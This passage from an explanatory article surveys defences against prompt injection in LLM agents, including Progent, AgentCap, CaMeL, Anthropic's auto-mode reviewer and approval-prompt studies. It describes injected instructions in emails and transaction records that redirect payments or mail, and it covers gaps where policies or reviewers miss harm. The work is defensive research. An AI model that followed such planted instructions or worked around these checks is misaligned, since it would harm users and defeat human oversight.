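allow send_slack_msg  when to is alice
```

Progent checks the call against the policy, not whether the attacker's email was malicious, so it would also have blocked the call if the agent had misread an innocent message. If the user had asked the agent to forward the inbox to that address, the policy could have included a rule allowing it, and the same call would have gone through.

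An attacker might try to trick the model that writes the policy into adding `send_email`. Progent therefore compares each proposed policy with the current one. If A(P) is the set of calls that policy P allows, a new policy P′ takes effect automatically only when

A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

which means that it allows nothing new. An SMT solver, a program that works out whether logical conditions can all be true together, makes this comparison, so persuasive wording can't influence it. Every other update needs approval from a person or from a setting that the developer has chosen in advance.

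### Progent's results

Shi and colleagues tested Progent on AgentDojo, a benchmark with simulated banking, Slack, travel and office tasks, in which attackers plant instructions in the data that the agent reads. Both the agent and the part of Progent that writes policies used GPT-4o. Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9% without a defence to 1.0%, and the agent still completed its ordinary tasks about as often. On a second benchmark, Agent Security Bench, it fell from 70.3% to 3.9%.

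In these tests, Progent automatically approved every proposed expansion of the policy to imitate a careless user, so the low figures don't depend on anybody reviewing the proposals. Most of the protection came from the first policy, which the model wrote before the agent had read any untrusted text. With that policy and no updates, 2.5% of the AgentDojo attacks succeeded.

When a person reviewed the policies, the figure fell to zero. However, Shi and colleagues assumed a reviewer with strong security awareness, who would never allow payments to arbitrary recipients. Only 6% of the policy updates needed approval, which would make careful review easier, but the test didn't measure how well an ordinary user would review them.

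They also left out two of the benchmark's travel attacks, in which planted text persuades the agent to choose a different but real hotel. The user asked the agent to book a hotel, so a rule about permitted tools can't block the attacker's choice without also blocking a good one.

### Checking where an argument came from

A payment assistant has to be able to send money, so its policy also has to restrict who receives it. The developer often can't list every future payee. *AgentCap* (Suresh and Gao, 2026) addresses this by recording where the payee value came from.

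Suppose a user asks the assistant to pay a bill, and an attacker has planted a payment instruction in a transaction record. The assistant calls the payment tool with the attacker's account number. AgentCap's policy marks the recipient as a sensitive argument and the text of the record as untrusted. Since the account number appears only in untrusted text, AgentCap blocks the payment. If the user had also given that number, the payment could go ahead.

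This resembles the tracing rule that OWASP proposed in its July 2023 draft and later dropped, but it tracks individual values rather than whole plugins. An agent can read a stranger's web page and still make a payment, as long as the payee's details come from a source the policy allows.

An approved call also gets a signed token, which the gateway in front of the tool checks before passing the call on. In the example banking policy, a token for sending money lasts 30 seconds and covers one call. The agent must first have obtained permission to check the balance. An agent can hand its token to another agent working for it, but the second agent is limited to the same action on the same account, with no more time or calls than the first had.

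Suresh and Gao ran all 949 attacks in the AgentDojo version they used and 1,054 attacks from another benchmark, InjecAgent. The table gives the results without and with AgentCap.

| Benchmark and model | Attacks that succeeded | User's tasks completed during attacks |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4o | 45.6% → 5.1% | 73.6% → 74.9% |
| AgentDojo, GPT-5.4 | 33.2% → 0% | 75.7% → 75.0% |
| InjecAgent, GPT-4o | 23.2% → 8.6% | 74.1% → 62.2% |
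| InjecAgent, GPT-5.4 | 12.0% → 0% | 73.0% → 65.4% |

Without an attack, AgentCap lowered the share of completed tasks by 3.1 to 11.7 percentage points. Suresh and Gao ran each condition only once, so small differences may be chance. They wrote the AgentDojo policies before running the tests but after reading the benchmark's descriptions of the user tasks. A company with a narrow product could write policies for known tasks in much the same way, but the maker of a general assistant doesn't know in advance what its users will ask.

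The AgentCap paper also tested Progent on the same attacks, with GPT-4o, and Progent did worse than its own paper had suggested. Progent completed 68.0% of tasks without an attack and 59.6% under attack, compared with 78.4% and 74.9% for AgentCap. The AgentCap paper attributes this to Progent's generated rules, which often allowed only the values the model had foreseen and so blocked legitimate calls with other values. The comparison comes from the makers of a rival system, but the explanation is plausible and applies to any policy written before the work begins.

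### Fixing the plan before reading anything

Another approach is to choose the agent's actions before it reads any untrusted text. Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, set out six designs, all meant to ensure that untrusted input cannot trigger a harmful action once an agent has read it.

If a user asks an assistant to email today's schedule to John Doe, the model in a plan-then-execute design first writes a plan with two tool calls, one to read today's calendar and one to email John Doe. The application then runs only those calls, so a malicious calendar entry can't add a third call or change the recipient, though it can still change what the email says.

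In the stricter "dual LLM" design, which OWASP's version 1.1 cited, the model without tools might find an email address in an untrusted document and store it under a label such as `$VAR$`. The planning model can ask the application to send a message to `$VAR$` but never sees the address. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) takes this further with CaMeL, a system in which the model writes a complete program from the user's request and ordinary code then runs it on the untrusted data.

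These designs give firmer guarantees than a filter that tries to recognise attacks, but they suit some jobs better than others. A shop's chatbot can choose from a fixed list of actions, but an agent working through the to-do list in Alice's email can't, because it has to read the email to find out what the job is. According to Shi and colleagues, CaMeL requires developers to change the agent's internals and makes the agent less useful, whereas developers can add Progent to an existing agent.

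Beurer-Kellner and colleagues think general-purpose agents built on current language models are unlikely to offer reliable guarantees. They suggest building agents for narrower jobs, which OWASP's advice on tools and functions also implies.

### Harm within the limits

Even a policy that works exactly as written can let harmful actions through. *NOMOS* (2026) describes a system that turns written policies into automatic checks on tool calls. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, the system cut attack success from 46.5% to zero with one model and from 44.1% to zero with another. But the benchmark counts an attack as successful only if it achieves the attacker's specific goal. In some of the attacks counted as failures, the injected text still made the agent send payments to approved payees. In another test, an agent emailed the user's passport and card numbers to an address the user had mentioned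 in the request, and the policy didn't forbid this.

*Bounded Agents* (2026) reports a harsher test, in which the researchers inserted the attacker's tool call themselves, as if the attacker fully controlled the model. Of 609 such attacks, 18 succeeded, or about 3%. In four of the 18, the policy lacked a rule against a particular combination of tools. The low success rate is good evidence for enforcing limits outside the model, since the model's own resistance played no part in the test.

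The remaining failures mostly come from incomplete policies and from harm that no rule about tools can prevent. Suresh and Gao found the same pattern in the attacks that got past AgentCap. Some only needed the agent to write something false, so there was no tool call to block. Others succeeded because the policy had not marked an argument as sensitive or a piece of text as untrusted.

Software developers see the same problem without any attacker, because permission to edit a folder also covers files the user didn't want changed. In *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), several practitioners described agents that stayed inside the workspace they were given but did more than they were asked.

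### What the limits cost

Stricter policies usually leave more tasks unfinished, and the number varies widely between systems. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) compares two policies on AgentDojo with a GPT-4o agent. With no attack, the agent completed 62.5% of its tasks under rules about where each argument came from, and 33.2% under rules about how information may flow between tools. It completed 83.7% with AgentDojo's own simple defence, which picks a list of allowed tools from the user's request.

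A strict limit can also do more harm than good. *aiAuthZ* (2026) tested an allow-list of payees with two 2026 models that already resisted every attack in a 20-case sample. The list prevented no additional attacks, and it cut completed tasks from 100% to 80% by blocking one legitimate payment to a new payee. The sample is very small, but the same mistake is easy to imagine in a real bank, where customers often pay someone for the first time.

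For an agent with access to important systems, strict controls may be worth using even if they block many legitimate requests. In *Separation of Duties for Privileged LLM Agents* (2026), checks on the agent's actions, together with a sandbox, cut attack success from 98.3% to 7.7%. The system wrongly refused 11.1% of legitimate requests, according to a case-by-case review that corrected an initial count of 20.4%. A separate experiment relied only on a prompt to make Claude Opus 5 follow the rules. This setup blocked one of 30 legitimate requests but allowed 53 of 59 attempts to get around the rules.

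An application can let the user override some refusals. For example, it could ask whether a new payee is genuine and make the payment if the user says yes. This recovers much of the lost usefulness, but the protection then depends on how carefully the user answers.

### Approving by habit

Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, by default asked for approval before running commands or changing files. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* reports that users accepted 93% of these requests, and the company's August 2026 article gives 97%. Users weren't necessarily careless, since most of the requests were probably harmless.

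Anthropic's experiment with 1,053 paid testers is better evidence. Partway through a coding session, the researchers replaced the text of one approval request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers (13.6%) rejected it. Testers blocked about 17% of these commands early in a session, but only about 5% after 50 or more prompts.

The same commands also went to Anthropic's "auto mode", in which a second model reviews the agent's actions in place of the user. It blocked 937 of them (89%), including 800 that the testers had approved. The testers blocked only six that auto mode had allowed, so using both would have stopped 943 commands and let 110 through.

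Anthropic has an interest in this result, because it sells the agent and wants people to let it run for longer. The testers were also working in a test environment, where they would not have lost their own files if they made a mistake. However, the test was realistic in placing a single dangerous request among many ordinary ones.

Other studies also find that people approve requests out of habit. *Options, Not Clicks* (2026) surveyed 16 users, and only three read permission prompts carefully. Thirteen chose "Always Allow" to make the prompts go away. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) examined 290 reports of agents mishandling files and found that user review played a part in 105. The user had turned on automatic approval in 80 of these, and the prompt gave too little information in 31. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but the command runs whatever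 code is in that file.

According to *From Delegation to Action Approval* (2026), usage data show that experienced users turn on automatic approval more often but also interrupt the agent more often. They seem to prefer watching the work as a whole to approving each step.

People did better in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), a study of 113 participants with no professional software background. Each supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions, seven of which went beyond what the user had asked for. One group approved actions one by one, a second relied on an automatic reviewer, and a third set rules in advance for spending money, sending information, deleting things and reading private data.

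Participants who set standing rules blocked the least overreach, 20.1 percentage points less than participants asked to approve every action and 14.5 points less than the automatic reviewer. They could set each rule to "allow", "ask" or "never", and chose "ask" for 114 of 140. When the agent asked, they usually said yes. They approved 133 of the 148 excessive actions that went through in this group.

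The 140 rules imply 35 participants in that group, so together they faced 245 excessive actions and blocked about 40% of them. The people asked to approve every action therefore blocked about 60%, far more than Anthropic's testers did. One likely reason is that more than a third of the requests in Yan's study deserved a refusal, which gave participants an incentive to stay alert. Each prompt also described the action, which is easier to judge than a line of code. Dangerous requests are rare in ordinary use, so people are much less likely to read each prompt carefully.

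### Which actions are worth an interruption?

If people give less attention to each prompt as the number grows, an application should save its prompts for actions that could do serious damage. OWASP advises asking before high-impact actions but gives only a few examples. Anthropic's default rules for auto mode are more specific. They cover four groups of actions:

- destroying data or sending it outside, such as deleting a large amount of cloud storage;
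- weakening security, for instance by turning off logging;
- using things the agent has no reason to trust, such as code from an unknown project or a password it happened to find;
- skipping a review or affecting other people, for example by changing a live service.

By contrast, auto mode lets the agent edit files inside the current project without any check, because developers can see and reverse those changes through version control. A developer of an email assistant could similarly let it label messages without a check but require one before it sends a message, because sending, unlike labelling, is not easy to undo.

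Anthropic's reviewer applies these rules with a language model, so it can make mistakes that Progent's fixed comparison can't. The reviewer missed 17% of 52 real cases in which Claude had gone further than the user wanted. In the cases it missed, it usually recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had agreed to it. For example, a request to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) doesn't give permission to overwrite the project's history. Anthropic still recommends that people review high-stakes changes to live infrastructure.

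The form of the approval request also matters. Claude Code users rejected only 3% of requests to approve a single action but 39% of Claude's plans. Part of the difference may be that users have opinions about the choices in a plan, but a plan also gives them one substantial thing to read. The agent can still depart from a plan after the user approves it, so the application would have to enforce the plan, as in the plan-then-execute design.

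A sandbox can make many approval prompts unnecessary. If a command can only touch a copy of the project and has no network access, nobody needs to approve it. According to *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent-Human Interaction Problem* (2026), Anthropic reports that sandboxing cut prompts in Claude Code by 84%. Sandboxing works only when the developer has set it up correctly, and tasks that use the network still need another check.

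Approval prompts can also offer better choices than yes, no and always. The ConLeash system in *Options, Not Clicks* lets a user approve a tool within a boundary, such as one folder. Users who click "Always Allow" without much thought then give the tool access to that folder instead of the whole disk.

### The argument for more agency

Larry Maccherone of Lumenize, who thinks excessive agency ranks too high, accepts in principle the advice to contain damage. But he told ReversingLabs he worries that security teams will respond by adding another gate, approval step or policy engine. A reviewer can inspect ordinary software before release because it stays the same, but can't approve an agent's behaviour in advance because it is new each time the agent runs. He would rather give the agent good feedback, so that it notices a failure quickly, finds the cause and adapts.

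The evidence on approval supports part of his case. Adding another approval prompt to a session that already has 50 would probably achieve little. The Progent rerun also shows that a policy can block good work that the policy's writer didn't foresee.

But a policy can limit the effects of an agent's behaviour without predicting that behaviour. In the inbox example, nobody foresaw the attacker's email, but Progent blocked the call because the task didn't require sending mail. Feedback comes after the first failure, which is much less acceptable when the failure is a stolen password than when it is a broken web page.

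When Progent or Anthropic's auto mode blocks a call, it tells the agent why, so the agent can look for another way to finish the job. An agent that keeps looking may find a way around the limit, so auto mode stops and asks the user after three refusals in a row or 20 in a session. An agent that repairs software could also have wide freedom in a test copy and need approval only to change the live system.

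### The Agent Control Standard

The studies above use different systems and policy formats. Progent uses JSON Schema, a general data format, while AgentCap has its own language. A team that adopts one can't easily move its rules to another.

On 2 September 2026, OWASP announced that its GenAI Security Project had received the Agent Control Standard as a donation. The project already had advice on agents' risks, identity, governance and testing, and OWASP says the standard extends this "toward practical runtime enforcement", meaning controls that operate while an agent runs. Rick Caccia of WitnessAI, which had just become a sponsor of the project, called it an important step.

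The release includes no test results for the standard. The studies above evaluate other systems, so their good results support checking actions outside the model but don't show that this standard works. A general standard also can't specify which payees a bank's assistant should accept or how large a refund a shop should allow. The developer still has to write those rules, and many of the remaining attacks succeeded because a rule was missing.

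A useful evaluation would run the same agents on the same attacks with and without the standard, and report both how many attacks succeeded and how many legitimate tasks the agents finished. Both counts are needed because a control that blocked every tool call would stop every attack and every legitimate task that needed one.
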